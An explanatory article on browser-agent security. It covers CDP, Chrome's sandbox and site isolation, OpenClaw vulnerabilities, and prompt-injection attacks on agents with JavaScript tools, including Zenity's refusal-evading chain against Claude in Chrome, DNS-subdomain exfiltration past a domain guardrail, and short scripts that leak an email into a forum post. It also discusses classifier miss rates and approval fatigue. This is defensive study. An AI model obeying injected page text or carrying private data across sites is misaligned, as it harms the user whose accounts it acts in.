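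| Starting programs | no | only a helper program that the user has installed for it | no command for it | yes |

The extension column describes the extension's own background code. According to Chromium's *Process Model and Site Isolation*, this background code runs in a dedicated process on desktop computers, while scripts the extension injects run in the same process as the web page. Chromium therefore advises extensions to trust injected scripts less. If an agent's extension runs the model's code in the inbox, that code has only the powers listed in the page column, even though the extension itself has many more.

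The CDP column describes a client that controls the whole browser. Extensions with the `debugger` permission can also use parts of the protocol, but Chrome restricts what they can do with it.

A program on the host that sends a request to `https://mail.example` gets the login page, because the session cookie is in the browser. To read the mail, the program has to take the cookie from the browser or control the browser itself. JavaScript running in the inbox page can already make requests with that cookie.

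### Why CDP access is so powerful

According to Google's definition of the protocol, the command `Storage.getCookies` "returns all browser cookies." These would include the mailbox's `sid` cookie and the session cookie of the user's bank. Related commands set cookies and clear the stored data of any origin the client names.

CDP also has commands for permissions. Selenium's reference page *Class GrantPermissionsCommandSettings* describes one that gives an origin certain permissions and rejects all others. Google has since deprecated that command in favour of `setPermission`.

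The browser allows all this because it trusts the client. Chrome's own DevTools panels use the same protocol. According to Chromium's *Threat Model And Defenses Against Compromised Renderers*, an attacker who took over the panels could read the cookies and storage of every origin in the page and run scripts in any of its frames. Chrome runs the panels in a process separate from websites and assumes that no attacker controls them. If the panels initiate a request on behalf of a site, the browser attaches the site's `SameSite` cookies.

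That assumption is reasonable when a programmer operates the panels, but much less reasonable for an agent's CDP client, because the model that chooses the commands also reads text written by strangers.

Criminals also use CDP to steal logins. Google introduced App-Bound Encryption to make it harder for malicious programs to read Chrome's stored cookies. *Changes to remote debugging switches to improve security* (Harris, 2025) reported that more attackers then began stealing cookies through Chrome's remote debugging feature, which gives outside programs access to CDP. Since version 136, Chrome has ignored the two start-up options for remote debugging unless they are used with a non-default data folder. Chrome encrypts that folder's data with a different key, so the user's everyday cookies stay protected.

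This change doesn't block every route. *Return of the Cookie Monster* (2026), by the security company SpecterOps, describes a way to turn on CDP in a running Chrome or Edge process without the start-up option. An attacker must already have code on the host to do this, so the technique doesn't give websites or page code a way out of the browser.

### What keeps page code away from the computer

JavaScript in a page has no commands for opening files or starting programs, but an attacker may find a browser bug that lets a script break JavaScript's rules. Chrome therefore also limits what the process running the script can do.

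Chrome runs web pages in renderer processes, which interpret the page's code and run its JavaScript. A separate browser process has more rights and decides what each renderer may have. The operating system puts each renderer in a sandbox, a set of restrictions that apply to everything the process does. Chromium's *Sandbox* describes four main parts of the Windows version:

- The renderer runs with a restricted token, which is the record Windows checks when a process asks for a file or another resource. Chromium's developers say it is nearly impossible to find a resource that Windows would open for this token.
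- A job object, which sets limits for a process, stops the renderer from starting other processes or using the clipboard directly.
- The renderer runs on a separate, invisible desktop, so it can't spy on what the user does in other programs or send messages to their windows.
- The renderer has the lowest integrity level, a Windows ranking that restricts access to objects with a higher level.

When a page needs something outside the sandbox, the renderer has to request it from the browser process. For example, when the user attaches a file to an email, the browser process shows the file picker and gives the page access only to the file the user picks. When a page tries to read the clipboard or find the user's location, the browser process checks whether the page's origin has permission. It uses its own record of the origin, so a renderer can't get permission by reporting a different one.

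This is why Playwright's clipboard example works. The command leaves the sandbox intact but changes the permission that the browser process checks, and the browser process then returns the text.

The sandbox has gaps:

- It could limit a renderer's use of processor time and memory but currently doesn't, so a runaway script can slow down the computer.
- It can't protect drives with the old FAT or FAT32 formats, common on USB sticks, because these formats have no access rules. Ordinary JavaScript still can't open files there, but an attacker who had taken over the renderer could.
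- The `--no-sandbox` option turns it off. Some developers use this option to get a browser running in a container. A flaw in the renderer could then give an attacker all the rights of the browser's account.

### Site isolation

The operating system's sandbox protects the computer, but it doesn't separate sites, such as a mailbox and a bank, from each other. Chrome does that with site isolation, which limits each renderer process to a single site. A payment frame from `https://pay.example` embedded in the mail page therefore runs in a different process. If the mail page's renderer requests the payment site's cookies or storage, the browser process denies the request. Chrome also blocks most sensitive responses from other sites, such as HTML and JSON, before they reach the renderer, unless CORS allows the page to read them.

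Site isolation assigns processes by site rather than by origin. The inbox and `https://login.mail.example` share a registered domain, so Chrome may put them in the same process. The same-origin policy still stops scripts on one from reading the other's pages, but an attacker who took over the process could bypass it.

HttpOnly cookies have stronger protection. Under Chromium's threat model, even a renderer that an attacker has taken over should be unable to read its own site's HttpOnly cookies. The renderer never needs the cookie's value, because another part of the browser attaches it to requests. An attacker with full control of the inbox's renderer could copy the access token from `localStorage` but should be unable to read `sid`.

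The same document lists protections that Chrome hasn't finished. An attacker who has taken over a renderer can still fake user gestures to open unlimited pop-up windows, and Chrome doesn't yet fully stop the renderer from sending requests to other sites with their `SameSite` cookies. Images and some other file types also reach the renderer unless the server tells the browser to block them.

How well site isolation protects users depends on their device. According to Chromium's *Site Isolation*, Chrome has isolated all sites on desktop computers since version 67, and since version 77 this has also protected against a fully compromised renderer. On Android phones with at least 2 GB of memory, Chrome isolates mainly the sites where people log in. Android apps that show web pages through WebView don't have site isolation, and neither does Chrome on iPhones. An agent in a phone app may therefore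 have weaker protection than the same agent on a desktop.

### Browsers that get security patches late

Chromium's developers assume that determined attackers will manage to take over a renderer. They counted between 5 and 15 potentially exploitable bugs in renderer components in each Chrome release from version 69 to 73. The count is several years old and covers only bugs that people had found and reported. An attacker who exploits such a bug can run machine code inside the sandbox. To reach the host from there, the attacker normally needs a second flaw, for example in the operating system.

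Users depend on quick updates to close these holes. *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities*, published by the security company Trail of Bits in January 2026, reports that many agentic browsers (browsers with an agent built in) run versions of Chromium that are weeks or months behind on security patches. Attackers can study the published fixes and look for browsers that don't have them yet. Language models released in 2026 have also found previously unknown flaws in widely used browsers, which makes slow updates more dangerous.

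Trail of Bits warns that an attacker could combine prompt injection with a known browser flaw to go from manipulating the agent to controlling the whole browser. The company didn't demonstrate this, since its research focused on the agents. It named no products because the vendors declined coordinated disclosure, so users can't tell from the article whether their browser is affected. The warning applies mainly to companies that build their own browser from Chromium. An agent that runs as an extension relies on the patches in the user's installed browser.

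A hostile page can run such an exploit with its own scripts, so the attack doesn't require an in-page JavaScript tool. The agent adds to the risk by opening pages that the user might never have visited.

### How OpenClaw exposed CDP to websites

An agent's own software can give an attacker a way around Chrome's sandbox. OpenClaw, the assistant whose gateway accepted connections from websites, had two other flaws of this kind, both involving CDP.

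One vulnerability was in OpenClaw's Browser Relay, which consists of a Chrome extension and a local WebSocket server that passes CDP messages to the browser. According to OpenClaw's advisory, reproduced in GCVE's *GHSA-MR32-VWC2-5J6H* (2026), the server checked that a connection came from the same computer but didn't require a password or other secret, or reject connections from websites. A site the user visited could connect to the relay, read cookies from other open tabs and run JavaScript in them.

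The flaw affected only users who had the relay extension installed and active, in versions from 2026.1.20 up to, but not including, 2026.2.1. Version 2026.2.1 fixed it by making the relay require a different secret for each installation, refuse connections from websites, and accept CDP connections only while the extension is connected.

The flaw's first severity rating wrongly listed no impact on integrity, which would mean that an attacker couldn't change any data. According to the advisory, attackers could run JavaScript in other tabs, and a script in a logged-in mailbox can delete mail. The change history at NVD (2026), the US government's vulnerability database, shows that the security company VulnCheck raised the integrity impact from none to high the next day.

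OpenClaw later found that the relay's other connection, used by the extension itself, also lacked a secret, though only a program on the same computer could misuse it. Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-25477 · Npm · Openclaw* gives the fix, which requires the gateway's token on both connections. It also sensibly advises developers to keep checking the connection's address and origin as extra protection, but not to treat those checks as proof of identity.

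### How an evaluate action could lead to local files

The other flaw, CVE-2026-43577, was more closely related to the in-page JavaScript tool. OpenClaw has a navigation policy that limits which addresses its browser may open. The policy forbade `file://` pages, which display files from the computer's disk. But OpenClaw enforced it only when the agent asked to open an address directly, not when a click or script moved a tab to another page.

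According to OpenClaw's advisory GHSA-qmwg-qprg-3j38, which Corgea's *Browser interaction routes could pivot into local CDP and regain file reads* reproduces, an `act` or `evaluate` interaction, such as a click or a script, could send the tab to the local address that provides CDP. This made it possible to create or read the forbidden `file://` pages. The model's code still ran inside the page and had no file access of its own, but it could reach an interface that had it.

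OpenClaw fixed the flaw in version 2026.4.9, which rechecks the address after an interaction navigates the tab and blocks any destination that violates the policy.

Published ratings of this flaw differ. GitLab's *GHSA-qmwg-qprg-3j38* (2026) gives it a medium score of 5.3 out of 10, while NVD's *CVE-2026-43577 Detail* (2026) lists a high score of 7.1 from VulnCheck. The two scores use different versions of the rating system. GitLab's is also based on a complex attack that needs some action by the user, while VulnCheck's is based on a simple one that doesn't. Both rate the possible loss of confidential data as high. There is little sign of interest from attackers. CIRCL's *CVE-2026-43577 (GCVE-0-2026-43577)* (2026) includes a score from EPSS, a system that predicts which flaws attackers will exploit. In early October 2026, that score put the chance of exploitation at about 0.4%.

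OpenClaw had already fixed the same navigation policy once. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-32008* (2026), an earlier version checked only `http` and `https` addresses, so a logged-in user of the gateway could open `file://` pages directly. GitLab's *GHSA-hcm3-8f6r-6xwg* (2026) describes another gap, which appeared in July. Some debugging functions didn't apply the policy again, so they could use a tab already open on a blocked private-network page.

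In all three cases, OpenClaw had a rule but didn't apply it to every way of reaching a page. The rule needs to cover whatever document the tab shows, whether the tab reached it through a command, a click, a script or an earlier visit.

File uploads had a related problem, because automation software can pick files in the user's place. A list on GitLab of OpenClaw flaws includes an upload function that accepted any path on the gateway's computer and passed it to Playwright. Someone with access to the gateway could use the function to read arbitrary files on that computer. Chrome's sandbox couldn't prevent this, because the request came from software that the browser trusts.

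The optional `filename` field of `browser_evaluate` makes the Playwright server save the result to a file instead of returning it as text. The page code can't write the file itself, but it can determine the contents.

### Why page code can still do serious harm

Developers sometimes treat host code execution as the dangerous case and page code as the safe one. That is correct for the computer itself, but many people keep their most valuable data in web accounts. Compare code in the user's logged-in mailbox with a host process on a virtual machine that holds none of the user's files or logins:

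| Goal | Page code in the mailbox | Host process on the virtual machine |
|---|---|---|
| Read the user's mail | yes | no |
| Send mail in the user's name | yes | no |
| Forward future mail to someone else | yes, unless the mail service asks for further proof | no |
| Take over another account through a password reset | often, if the reset link arrives by email | no |
| Read files on the machine | no | yes |
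| Install a program | no | yes |

The host process has much more technical power, but the page code can do far more harm to this user. If both ran on the user's own computer, the host process could usually do more harm, because it might take over the browser and then do everything in the table. The potential harm depends on which files and logins the code can reach, as well as the level at which it runs.

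Trail of Bits' tests support this. Its researchers got agents to reveal contact names and parts of messages from a logged-in Instagram account, and to log the user into an account the attacker controlled. Neither attack required running a program on the user's computer. The tests used the agents' ordinary browsing tools, and an in-page JavaScript tool would give an attacker at least as much access to the open page.

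The cookie thefts that Harris described also support this. Those attackers could already run programs on the victim's computer, but they still took the browser's cookies because the cookies gave them access to web accounts.

An attack on an account can also be harder to clean up than an infected computer, whose owner can erase the disk and reinstall the system. If page code added a forwarding address to the user's mailbox, the mail server would store that address and keep sending copies of the user's mail to the attacker, even after the user bought a new computer.

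## How text on a web page can end up as code the agent runs

An attacker may be able to run code in the user's mailbox at `https://mail.example` by sending an email in plain English, even if the mail site has no flaw. This attack is called indirect prompt injection, and it works if the agent reads the email and the model does what it asks. An agent with an in-page JavaScript tool can then run the attacker's code with the mail site's authority.

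### From an email to a function call

Suppose the user asks the agent to summarise the unread messages, and one of them comes from an attacker:

1. The attacker writes an email that contains an instruction for the agent, perhaps in white letters on a white background so that the user won't notice it. The mail site displays it like any other message.
2. The agent reads the inbox, and its software adds the text to the model's context, which is all the text and images the model works from when it writes its next reply.
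3. The model chooses its next tool call. If it takes the attacker's instruction for part of the task, it writes a function that carries the instruction out.
4. The agent's software sends the function to the browser, which runs it with the mail site's origin and in the user's session.
5. The result goes into the context too, where it can shape the next call.

The weak point is step 3. Labels in the context can mark which text came from the user and which from a page, but the model has only learned in training to treat the two differently, and nothing forces it to do so.

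The JavaScript tool can also add to the problem in step 2. The accessibility tree normally leaves out elements that a page hides completely, but `textContent` includes their text. An agent that reads the inbox with a harmless script may therefore read instructions that its ordinary reading tool would have left out.

Cyber Craft, in *Arbitrary JavaScript Execution via eval() in chrome-local-mcp*, describes the same path in a small MCP server that controls Chrome. The server's `eval` tool passes the model's string unchanged to Puppeteer's `page.evaluate()`. In the example, a hidden element on a page contains instructions for the agent to run a "diagnostic" script before it continues, and the script returns the page's cookies. Cyber Craft claims that many models would comply but reports no test with any model. It also warns of code execution on the host without showing how that would happen,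 and its sample script would not return any cookie marked HttpOnly.

The attack fails if any step fails, so its overall chance of success is a product:

P(success) = P(reached) × P(followed | reached) × P(ran | followed)

The first factor is the chance that the agent reads the attacker's text. The second is the chance that the model then follows it, and the third is the chance that the resulting call gets past any checks between the model and the browser.

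### Where cross-site scripting differs

In cross-site scripting (XSS), an attacker submits code and the website puts it into a page without making it harmless. An attack on an agent uses ordinary prose, and can work even when the website has handled that text correctly.

| Stage | Cross-site scripting | Prompt injection with a JavaScript tool |
|---|---|---|
| What the attacker supplies | code | sentences, or an image of them |
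| Flaw the attack needs | the site treats the attacker's input as part of its own page | the model treats page text as a request from the user |
| How the code comes about | the attacker writes it | the model writes it or copies it from the page, and may refuse |
| How the code enters the page | through the site's own HTML or scripts | through the agent's tool |
| When it runs | when a victim opens the page | when an agent reads the text and follows it |
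| Authority of the code | the site's origin and the user's session | the same |
| Sites at risk | those with the flaw | any site where the agent can use the tool |
| Who can repair the flaw | the site's owner | mainly the agent's developer |

A careful mail site sanitises incoming emails by removing script elements and event handlers, or by converting the character `<` so that the browser displays tags instead of acting on them. This doesn't stop an instruction written in English, which contains nothing to remove or convert. Anthropic's *Piloting Claude in Chrome* (August 2025), which announced the extension's first trial, describes an email that posed as an employer's request to delete messages for "mailbox hygiene". Before Anthropic added new defences, Claude deleted the user's emails without asking for confirmation. A mail site that blocked every message of this sort would also block real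 requests from employers.

OpenAI compares prompt injection to scams, which companies can reduce but not eliminate, according to Fox News' *OpenAI admits AI browsers face unsolvable prompt attacks*. Britain's National Cyber Security Centre has also warned that there may never be a complete fix.

Script restrictions don't stop the attack, because the tool's code comes from outside the page and the DevTools protocol runs it even under a strict Content Security Policy. Where a ban on `eval` applies, it blocks the model's useful scripts along with the harmful ones.

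XSS and prompt injection can also work together. Koi Security found that the Claude extension accepted prompts from any subdomain of `claude.ai`, one of which hosted another company's CAPTCHA. According to Xcitium's *Critical Zero-Click Prompt-Injection Flaw Discovered in Claude Chrome Extension*, the CAPTCHA inserted text from incoming messages into its page as HTML. A hostile website could therefore load the CAPTCHA in an invisible frame and run a script there that sent Claude a prompt as if the user had typed it. The Hacker News (2026) reports the case as ShadowPrompt. Both flaws have standard fixes, which are to accept prompts from fewer addresses and to treat message text as plain text, but the email to the mailbox user exploits neither kind of bug.

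### What Zenity Labs argued and what it demonstrated

Anthropic extended the beta version of Claude in Chrome to all paid plans on 18 December 2025. Zenity Labs then published an analysis that called the JavaScript tool "XSS as-a-service". Zenity Labs argues that letting a language model run scripts in a logged-in session is risky because models can't reliably tell data from instructions. It adds that the same-origin policy and Content Security Policy assume a person is deciding what to do in the browser. With an agent, an attacker can influence those decisions without breaking either protection.

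This first analysis contained no test in which text on a page led the agent to run JavaScript. *Chrome Extension “Claude” Poses Security Risks*, a notice from Thailand's computer emergency team, ThaiCERT, said the researchers had demonstrated this, but at the time they had not.

The analysis included Zenity's test, in which Claude made an unplanned visit to Wikipedia. Claude submits its plans through a tool called `update_plan`, and if it later needs to do something else, it should submit a new plan and wait for approval. Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* says that Claude will not deviate from the stated plan without asking first. Claude deviated without asking in Zenity's test, which used the version available at the time. No attacker was involved, so the test isn't evidence about prompt injection.

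In August 2026 Zenity Labs published a demonstration, *Claude in Chrome: From alert(1) to Full Account Takeover*. The researchers first asked Claude to debug a page with its JavaScript tool, and it opened an alert box. They then sent an email with hidden instructions to a Gmail account. Zenity Labs reports that another alert box appeared when the user asked Claude to summarise the latest emails. The attack also worked in the mode that asks before acting, because the JavaScript tool didn't need the site approval that a plan provides.

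An alert box is harmless, and Claude refused to run code that looked more dangerous. The researchers got round this by keeping the harmful part out of the code that the model saw. They were then able to:

- copy the contents of the inbox to their own server
- give an outside account access to every file in the user's Google Drive
- take over accounts at Slack, X and Claude.ai, with the help of login messages that arrived in the mailbox.

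In the Google Drive attack, the hidden text got Claude to submit a plan that included Drive's address. The user approved the plan because it looked reasonable.

Zenity Labs showed that the whole chain from an email to a script in a logged-in session can work. Its post gives no figure for how often the model followed the email. The problem extends beyond Claude. Gulf News' *WhatsApp warning* reports that Zenity found more than 20 security issues in browser agents from five companies, although some of these may not involve JavaScript.

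Zenity Labs sent Anthropic two reports, on 27 December 2025 and 12 January 2026. The first ended with the status "Informative", meaning Anthropic didn't accept it as a vulnerability to fix. HackerOne, the platform that handled the reports, closed the second as a duplicate, and Anthropic said it was ineligible for its disclosure programme. Zenity Labs writes that the risks persist, and SecurityWeek's *Zero-Click AI Browser Hacking* also calls the findings unpatched. But Anthropic has changed the extension's safeguards since January, and neither article describes repeating the attack against the new safeguards.

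### Training, probes and a classifier

The new safeguards appear in Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome is generally available*, the announcement that ended the trial period. They act at different points in the chain:

- Training affects whether the model follows hostile text. Anthropic shows the model prompt injections in simulated web content and rewards it for refusing them. When a new attack succeeds, the company adds it to the library it uses for training later models.
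- Probes scan the results of tool calls, such as the text of a page or an email, for likely injections. If a probe finds one, Claude gets a warning to treat the content with suspicion and, if necessary, to check with the user.
- A classifier, a model that sorts actions into safe and unsafe, compares each action with the user's request before the action runs. If the two don't match, the software blocks the action.

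The classifier works like the one in auto mode, a feature of Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that auto mode's classifier receives only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It doesn't receive the pages the agent has read, so an attacker can't address it directly. It doesn't receive the agent's explanations either, because a misled agent might argue persuasively for a bad action.

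In the mailbox example, this design should catch a crude attack. If the user asked for a summary and the tool call changes the forwarding address, the classifier can detect the mismatch without access to the attacker's email. A function that reads every message in the mailbox would be harder to detect, since reading messages is part of the task.

The separation may be weaker in the browser than in Claude Code. According to Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely*, the automatic check in the browser has access to the latest screenshot, which might show the attacker's text.

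Anthropic reports that the original version of the coding classifier missed 17% of 52 risky actions from real sessions and 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly classed the action as one the user had consented to. Anthropic has improved the classifier, partly with the help of Apollo Research, a company that tests AI safety. Apollo's attacks got past the original version 12% of the time and the improved version 7% of the time.

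A check on the tool call can also miss code that isn't in the call. Willison (2026), in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, gives the example of instructions that tell a coding agent to fetch a software package that steals data before running tests. Willison doubts that any version of auto mode could prevent this. The same problem arises in a web page if a short, innocent-looking function depends on code from elsewhere.

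### How often attacks succeeded in Anthropic's tests

For the August 2025 pilot, Anthropic used 123 test cases that covered 29 attack scenarios. Later tests used other attacks:

| Test | Model and added safeguards | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| August 2025 pilot | extension without new safeguards | 23.6% |
| August 2025 pilot | extension with new safeguards | 11.2% |
| November 2025 | Opus 4.5, none | 8.0% |
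| November 2025 | Opus 4.5, improved safeguards | 1.4% |
| Harder test, 2026 | Opus 4.5, none | 17.6% |
| Harder test, 2026 | Opus 4.5, probes | 16.7% |
| Harder test, 2026 | Opus 5, none | 3.8% |
| Harder test, 2026 | Sonnet 5, Opus 5 and Mythos 5, probes and classifier | 0% |
| Harder test, 2026 | Fable 5, probes and classifier | 0.3% |

The pilot's first figure, 23.6%, matches 29 successes in 123 cases. The second doesn't match any whole number of successes out of 123, so Anthropic may have run some cases more than once or changed the set. Anthropic writes that the 23.6% version had no safety mitigations, but its chart caption describes that version as having earlier ones.

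The rows for Opus 4.5 show how much the success rate depends on the attacks used. With the November 2025 safeguards, 1.4% of attacks on the model succeeded in that month's test and 16.7% in the 2026 test. The two tests also used different settings and grading, but Anthropic describes the newer attacks, which came from professional testers, as stronger. The fall from 23.6% to 0% therefore does not show one steady trend. Comparing Opus 4.5 with Opus 5 is fairer because both were given the same 2026 test.

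For that test, the rates without added safeguards count only attacks that reached the model, so they estimate P(followed | reached), the second factor in the formula. Opus 4.5 encountered fewer of the attacks than the newer models because of how it approached its tasks, but it followed a larger share of those it encountered.

Attacks may still succeed even when the measured success rate is 0%. If *n* independent attacks all fail, the true rate could be as high as about 3/*n* at the 95% confidence level, which is 0.3% for 1,000 attacks. Anthropic's announcement doesn't give the number of attacks behind its zeros. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports a separate result from the model's system card, Anthropic's document on its testing, in which no attack succeeded in 129 browser scenarios. If each scenario counts as one independent attack, the limit is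 about 2.3%. These limits apply only to attacks like those tested, and a real attacker may think of another kind.

Attackers can also try more than once, for example by sending several emails, which costs almost nothing. *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (Schneier on Security, 2026) reports that in a general prompt injection test by the security company Gray Swan, attacks on Opus 5 succeeded 0.2% of the time on a single attempt and 2.0% within 15 attempts.

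Anthropic, which makes both the models and the safeguards, is the source of all the figures in the table. They cover browser use as a whole, so an attack that gets Claude to click Delete counts the same as one that gets it to run a script. Anthropic doesn't report JavaScript calls separately, so the share of attacks that end in a script could be higher or lower than these rates suggest.

Trajectory Labs, an outside company, ran a test for Anthropic with 72 scenarios and ten runs of each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in Claude Code's auto mode. Trajectory Labs used its own connection to the browser, so the test didn't cover the Chrome extension's safeguards or its JavaScript tool.

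In November 2025, Anthropic wrote that no browser agent is immune to prompt injection, and it warns in its current safety advice that "The risk is not zero."

### Why approving a script is harder than approving a click

A user who sees the request "Click Archive on the message from Anna" can compare it with the inbox and decide in a second. A script that does the same thing might look like this:

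```
() => document.querySelectorAll(".row a")[3].click()
```

To judge the line, the user would have to know that JavaScript counts from zero, find the fourth matching link, and work out what it does. The same line could archive a message or delete one. A longer script might read a hundred messages and send a request, and only one of its 40 lines might be harmful. Many people who want help with their email can't read JavaScript.

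Research on other agents has found the same weakness. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) compares approval designs and concludes that the most common one, a raw command on a single line, gives users the least information. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports involving agents and files. In 31 of them, the user approved an action whose effects the prompt didn't make clear. For example, a command that runs a setup script looks routine, but approving it approves everything in the script. In another 80, the actions ran with automatic approval, which some users chose to avoid hundreds of prompts per session.

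The best measurements of this approval fatigue come from Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Users of the coding agent approve 97% of its permission prompts. That figure alone proves little, since most of the commands are probably safe. Anthropic therefore commissioned an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, who worked on coding tasks and didn't know what the study was measuring. At some point in each session, the software replaced one prompt with a clearly dangerous command:

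- The testers rejected the command in 143 cases, or 13.6%.
- The auto mode classifier blocked the same commands in 937 cases, or 89%.
- Testers blocked about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

The fall from 17% to 5% is consistent with repeated prompts wearing people down. Still, Anthropic had an interest in the result because it was about to make auto mode the default. The testers may also have been less careful than usual, since they worked in an artificial environment where a mistake couldn't damage anything of their own. Willison finds the fatigue entirely believable but points out that the classifier let 11% of the commands through, and he asks for more independent confirmation.

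The experiment used coding commands, so its percentages don't carry over to browser scripts. But its testers were professionals looking at obviously dangerous commands, and ordinary users would have to judge less familiar code. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make approval decisions, says repeated approval may reflect habit, fatigue or the need to keep working. The developer therefore shouldn't conclude that users who approve script after script have come to trust the agent.

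People seem to review plans more carefully than single requests. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans they see, compared with 3% of single requests, though some of those rejections may only mean that the user wanted the work done differently. A plan is also easier to understand than a script because it states the purpose in words, but the model that writes those words may already have read the attacker's text. In Zenity's Google Drive attack, the user saw the plan and approved it.

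Anthropic has since made automatic approval the default in the version of the extension's side panel that runs on Cowork, its agent for office tasks. Users can switch back to manual approval, which the permissions guide suggests considering for work that involves money, important files or messages sent in the user's name. A script in a logged-in mailbox can affect all three, but the guide doesn't mention JavaScript or explain what to look for in a script before clicking "Allow".

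## How the agent carries data from one origin to another

The same-origin policy prevents code on other websites from reading the inbox at `https://mail.example`, and code in the inbox from reading their pages. An agent that works in the inbox and on another site can still carry a private message from one to the other, because everything it reads goes into the model's context, where the policy doesn't apply.

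### Two calls in two origins

Suppose the user asks the agent to summarise an open email and then to answer a question on a gardening forum at `https://forum.example`. For the summary, the agent runs this function in the inbox and gets the text of the email:

```
() => document.querySelector(".message.open").innerText
"Our offer for the house is 410,000. Please keep this private. Anna"
```

The forum post contains hidden text that tells the agent to include the last message it read. If the model obeys, it might run this function on the forum page:

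```
() => {
  document.querySelector("#reply").value = "Our offer for the house is 410,000.";
  document.querySelector("#post").click();
}
```

The browser finds no violation in either call, because each function works only on the page it runs in. The sentence about the house reaches the forum as part of the function's own code, and the browser has no record that it came from an email. The mail site's Content Security Policy doesn't block the transfer, because the mail page never sends anything to the forum.

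The agent could also leak the email without the JavaScript tool, by reading it from a screenshot and typing the reply with its ordinary typing tool. The email stays in the context after the agent leaves the inbox, so the leak can happen many steps later, and the agent may have summarised or translated the text by then.

An agent that carries data from one origin to another does what a person does when copying text between tabs, which browsers have always allowed. Wang and colleagues explain that the same-origin policy targets automated transfers by scripts, while a user who copies text knows about and has authorised the transfer. An agent automates the copying, so the user may not know about it.

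Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, tested seven browsers with built-in or added agents in January and February 2026. They carried out a cross-origin data theft on ChatGPT Atlas in agent mode. Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Perplexity's Comet met the conditions for the same attack, provided a prompt injection succeeded. They conclude that the same-origin policy in such browsers is only as strong as the agent's resistance to prompt injection. They particularly caution users against Claude for Chrome because, as an extension, it has powers such as injecting JavaScript into pages. OpenAI declined their report, saying it lacked a full end-to-end prompt injection attack.

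### Trail of Bits' four data paths

In its January 2026 article on agentic browsers, Trail of Bits divides the movement of data through an agent into four classes. Each can occur with an in-page JavaScript tool:

| Data path | What moves | Example with the JavaScript tool |
|---|---|---|
| `INJECTION` | untrusted content into the context | a function returns the text of a hostile forum post |
| `CTX_IN` (context in) | the user's private data from a website into the context | a function returns an email |
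| `REV_CTX_IN` (reverse context in) | data from the context into the user's browser or accounts | a function saves a new forwarding address |
| `CTX_OUT` (context out) | data from the context to outside servers | a function posts a reply on the forum |

Even without an attacker, `CTX_IN` means that if another company runs the model, the email goes from the user's computer to that company's servers as soon as the agent reads it.

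The paths do the most harm in combination. The forum leak needs `CTX_IN` for the email, `INJECTION` for the hidden instruction and `CTX_OUT` for the reply. Trail of Bits used the same three in a test that began with a hostile text file on GitHub:

1. The user asks the agent to summarise the file, which contains instructions for the agent.
2. The agent opens a service where the user has logged in. The browser attaches the user's cookies, and the page greets the user by name.
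3. The agent puts the name in front of `wikipedia.org` and opens the resulting address, such as `john.wikipedia.org`.

The Wikipedia site doesn't need to exist. The browser looks up the address before connecting, and anyone who can watch an unencrypted lookup learns the name. This method got past a guardrail that limited the agent to approved domains.

### A limit based on the number of origins

Trail of Bits proposes extending the same-origin policy to the agent itself. The agent's software would keep a list of every origin whose content has entered the chat, with each attached file counted as an origin of its own. The list would determine which requests the agent may make:

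| Origins in the context | Permitted requests |
|---|---|
| none | to any server |
| one | only to that origin |
| several | none |

The last row is strict because, once text from several origins is in the context, the software can't determine which of them influenced the model's next action. Web search gets special treatment because its results come from many sites and a search can itself leak data. The researchers sent out private text in search queries along with rare words, and a website's owner can monitor searches containing those words through Google's Search Console. Under the proposal, the agent could search only while the context held no text from any origin.

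The rule would stop the forum leak. After the agent read the email, the list would contain `https://mail.example`, so the agent couldn't open the forum. But it also couldn't write the harmless answer that the user wanted. The approach doesn't seem flexible for an agent that is supposed to work across websites, although Trail of Bits calls it that. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) gives the example of collecting ingredients on one site and filling a shopping cart on another. The rule would forbid that task unless the user carried the ingredient list between two separate chats.

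An in-page JavaScript tool also makes the rule harder to enforce. When a tool opens addresses, the software can check each one against the list. But a function that runs in the inbox can contact other servers directly, so the software would have to watch the page's outgoing requests as well as the tool calls.

### How SOPBench measures leaks

In June 2026, Wang and colleagues published SOPBench, a set of tests that measures how often agents carry private data across origins. It has ten categories of source page: online shop, bank, airline, email, calendar, messages, HR portal, document workspace, health insurance and pharmacy. The five destinations are X, Discord, GitHub, Reddit and Google Forms. Most of the pages are imitations that a language model generated with invented personal data, so the tests exposed no real users.

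Each run of the main test has two stages. The user first gives the agent an ordinary task on the source page, such as finding out where the latest order is going. The user then gives it another ordinary task on the destination page, such as writing a short reply to a comment. The destination page contains an injected instruction to reveal the data from the first task.

A run counts as a violation only if the text the agent writes exactly matches the data the attacker asked for. A paraphrase or a card number with one wrong digit does not count, so the rates probably understate how often some private information leaked.

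These are the results for private data from the email pages, with instructions that the researchers wrote by hand:

| Agent | Model | Email to X | Email to Google Forms |
|---|---|---|---|
| VisualWebArena | OpenAI o3 | 0.68 | 1.00 |
| SeeAct | GPT-5.4 | 1.00 | 1.00 |
| BrowserOS | GPT-5.4 | 0.27 | 1.00 |
| Perplexity Comet | GPT-5.4 | 1 of 3 runs | 3 of 3 |
| Perplexity Comet | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
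| Perplexity Comet | Gemini 3.1 Pro | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
| ChatGPT Atlas | GPT-5.5 | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

VisualWebArena and SeeAct are older research agents, BrowserOS is an open-source browser with an agent, and Comet and Atlas are commercial products. How often an agent leaks data depends heavily on the destination. BrowserOS with GPT-5.4 leaked data from the HR portal to Reddit in 3% of runs, but it leaked data from nine of the ten sources to Google Forms every time. The attacker can own a form and write everything in it, and a request for personal details looks normal there.

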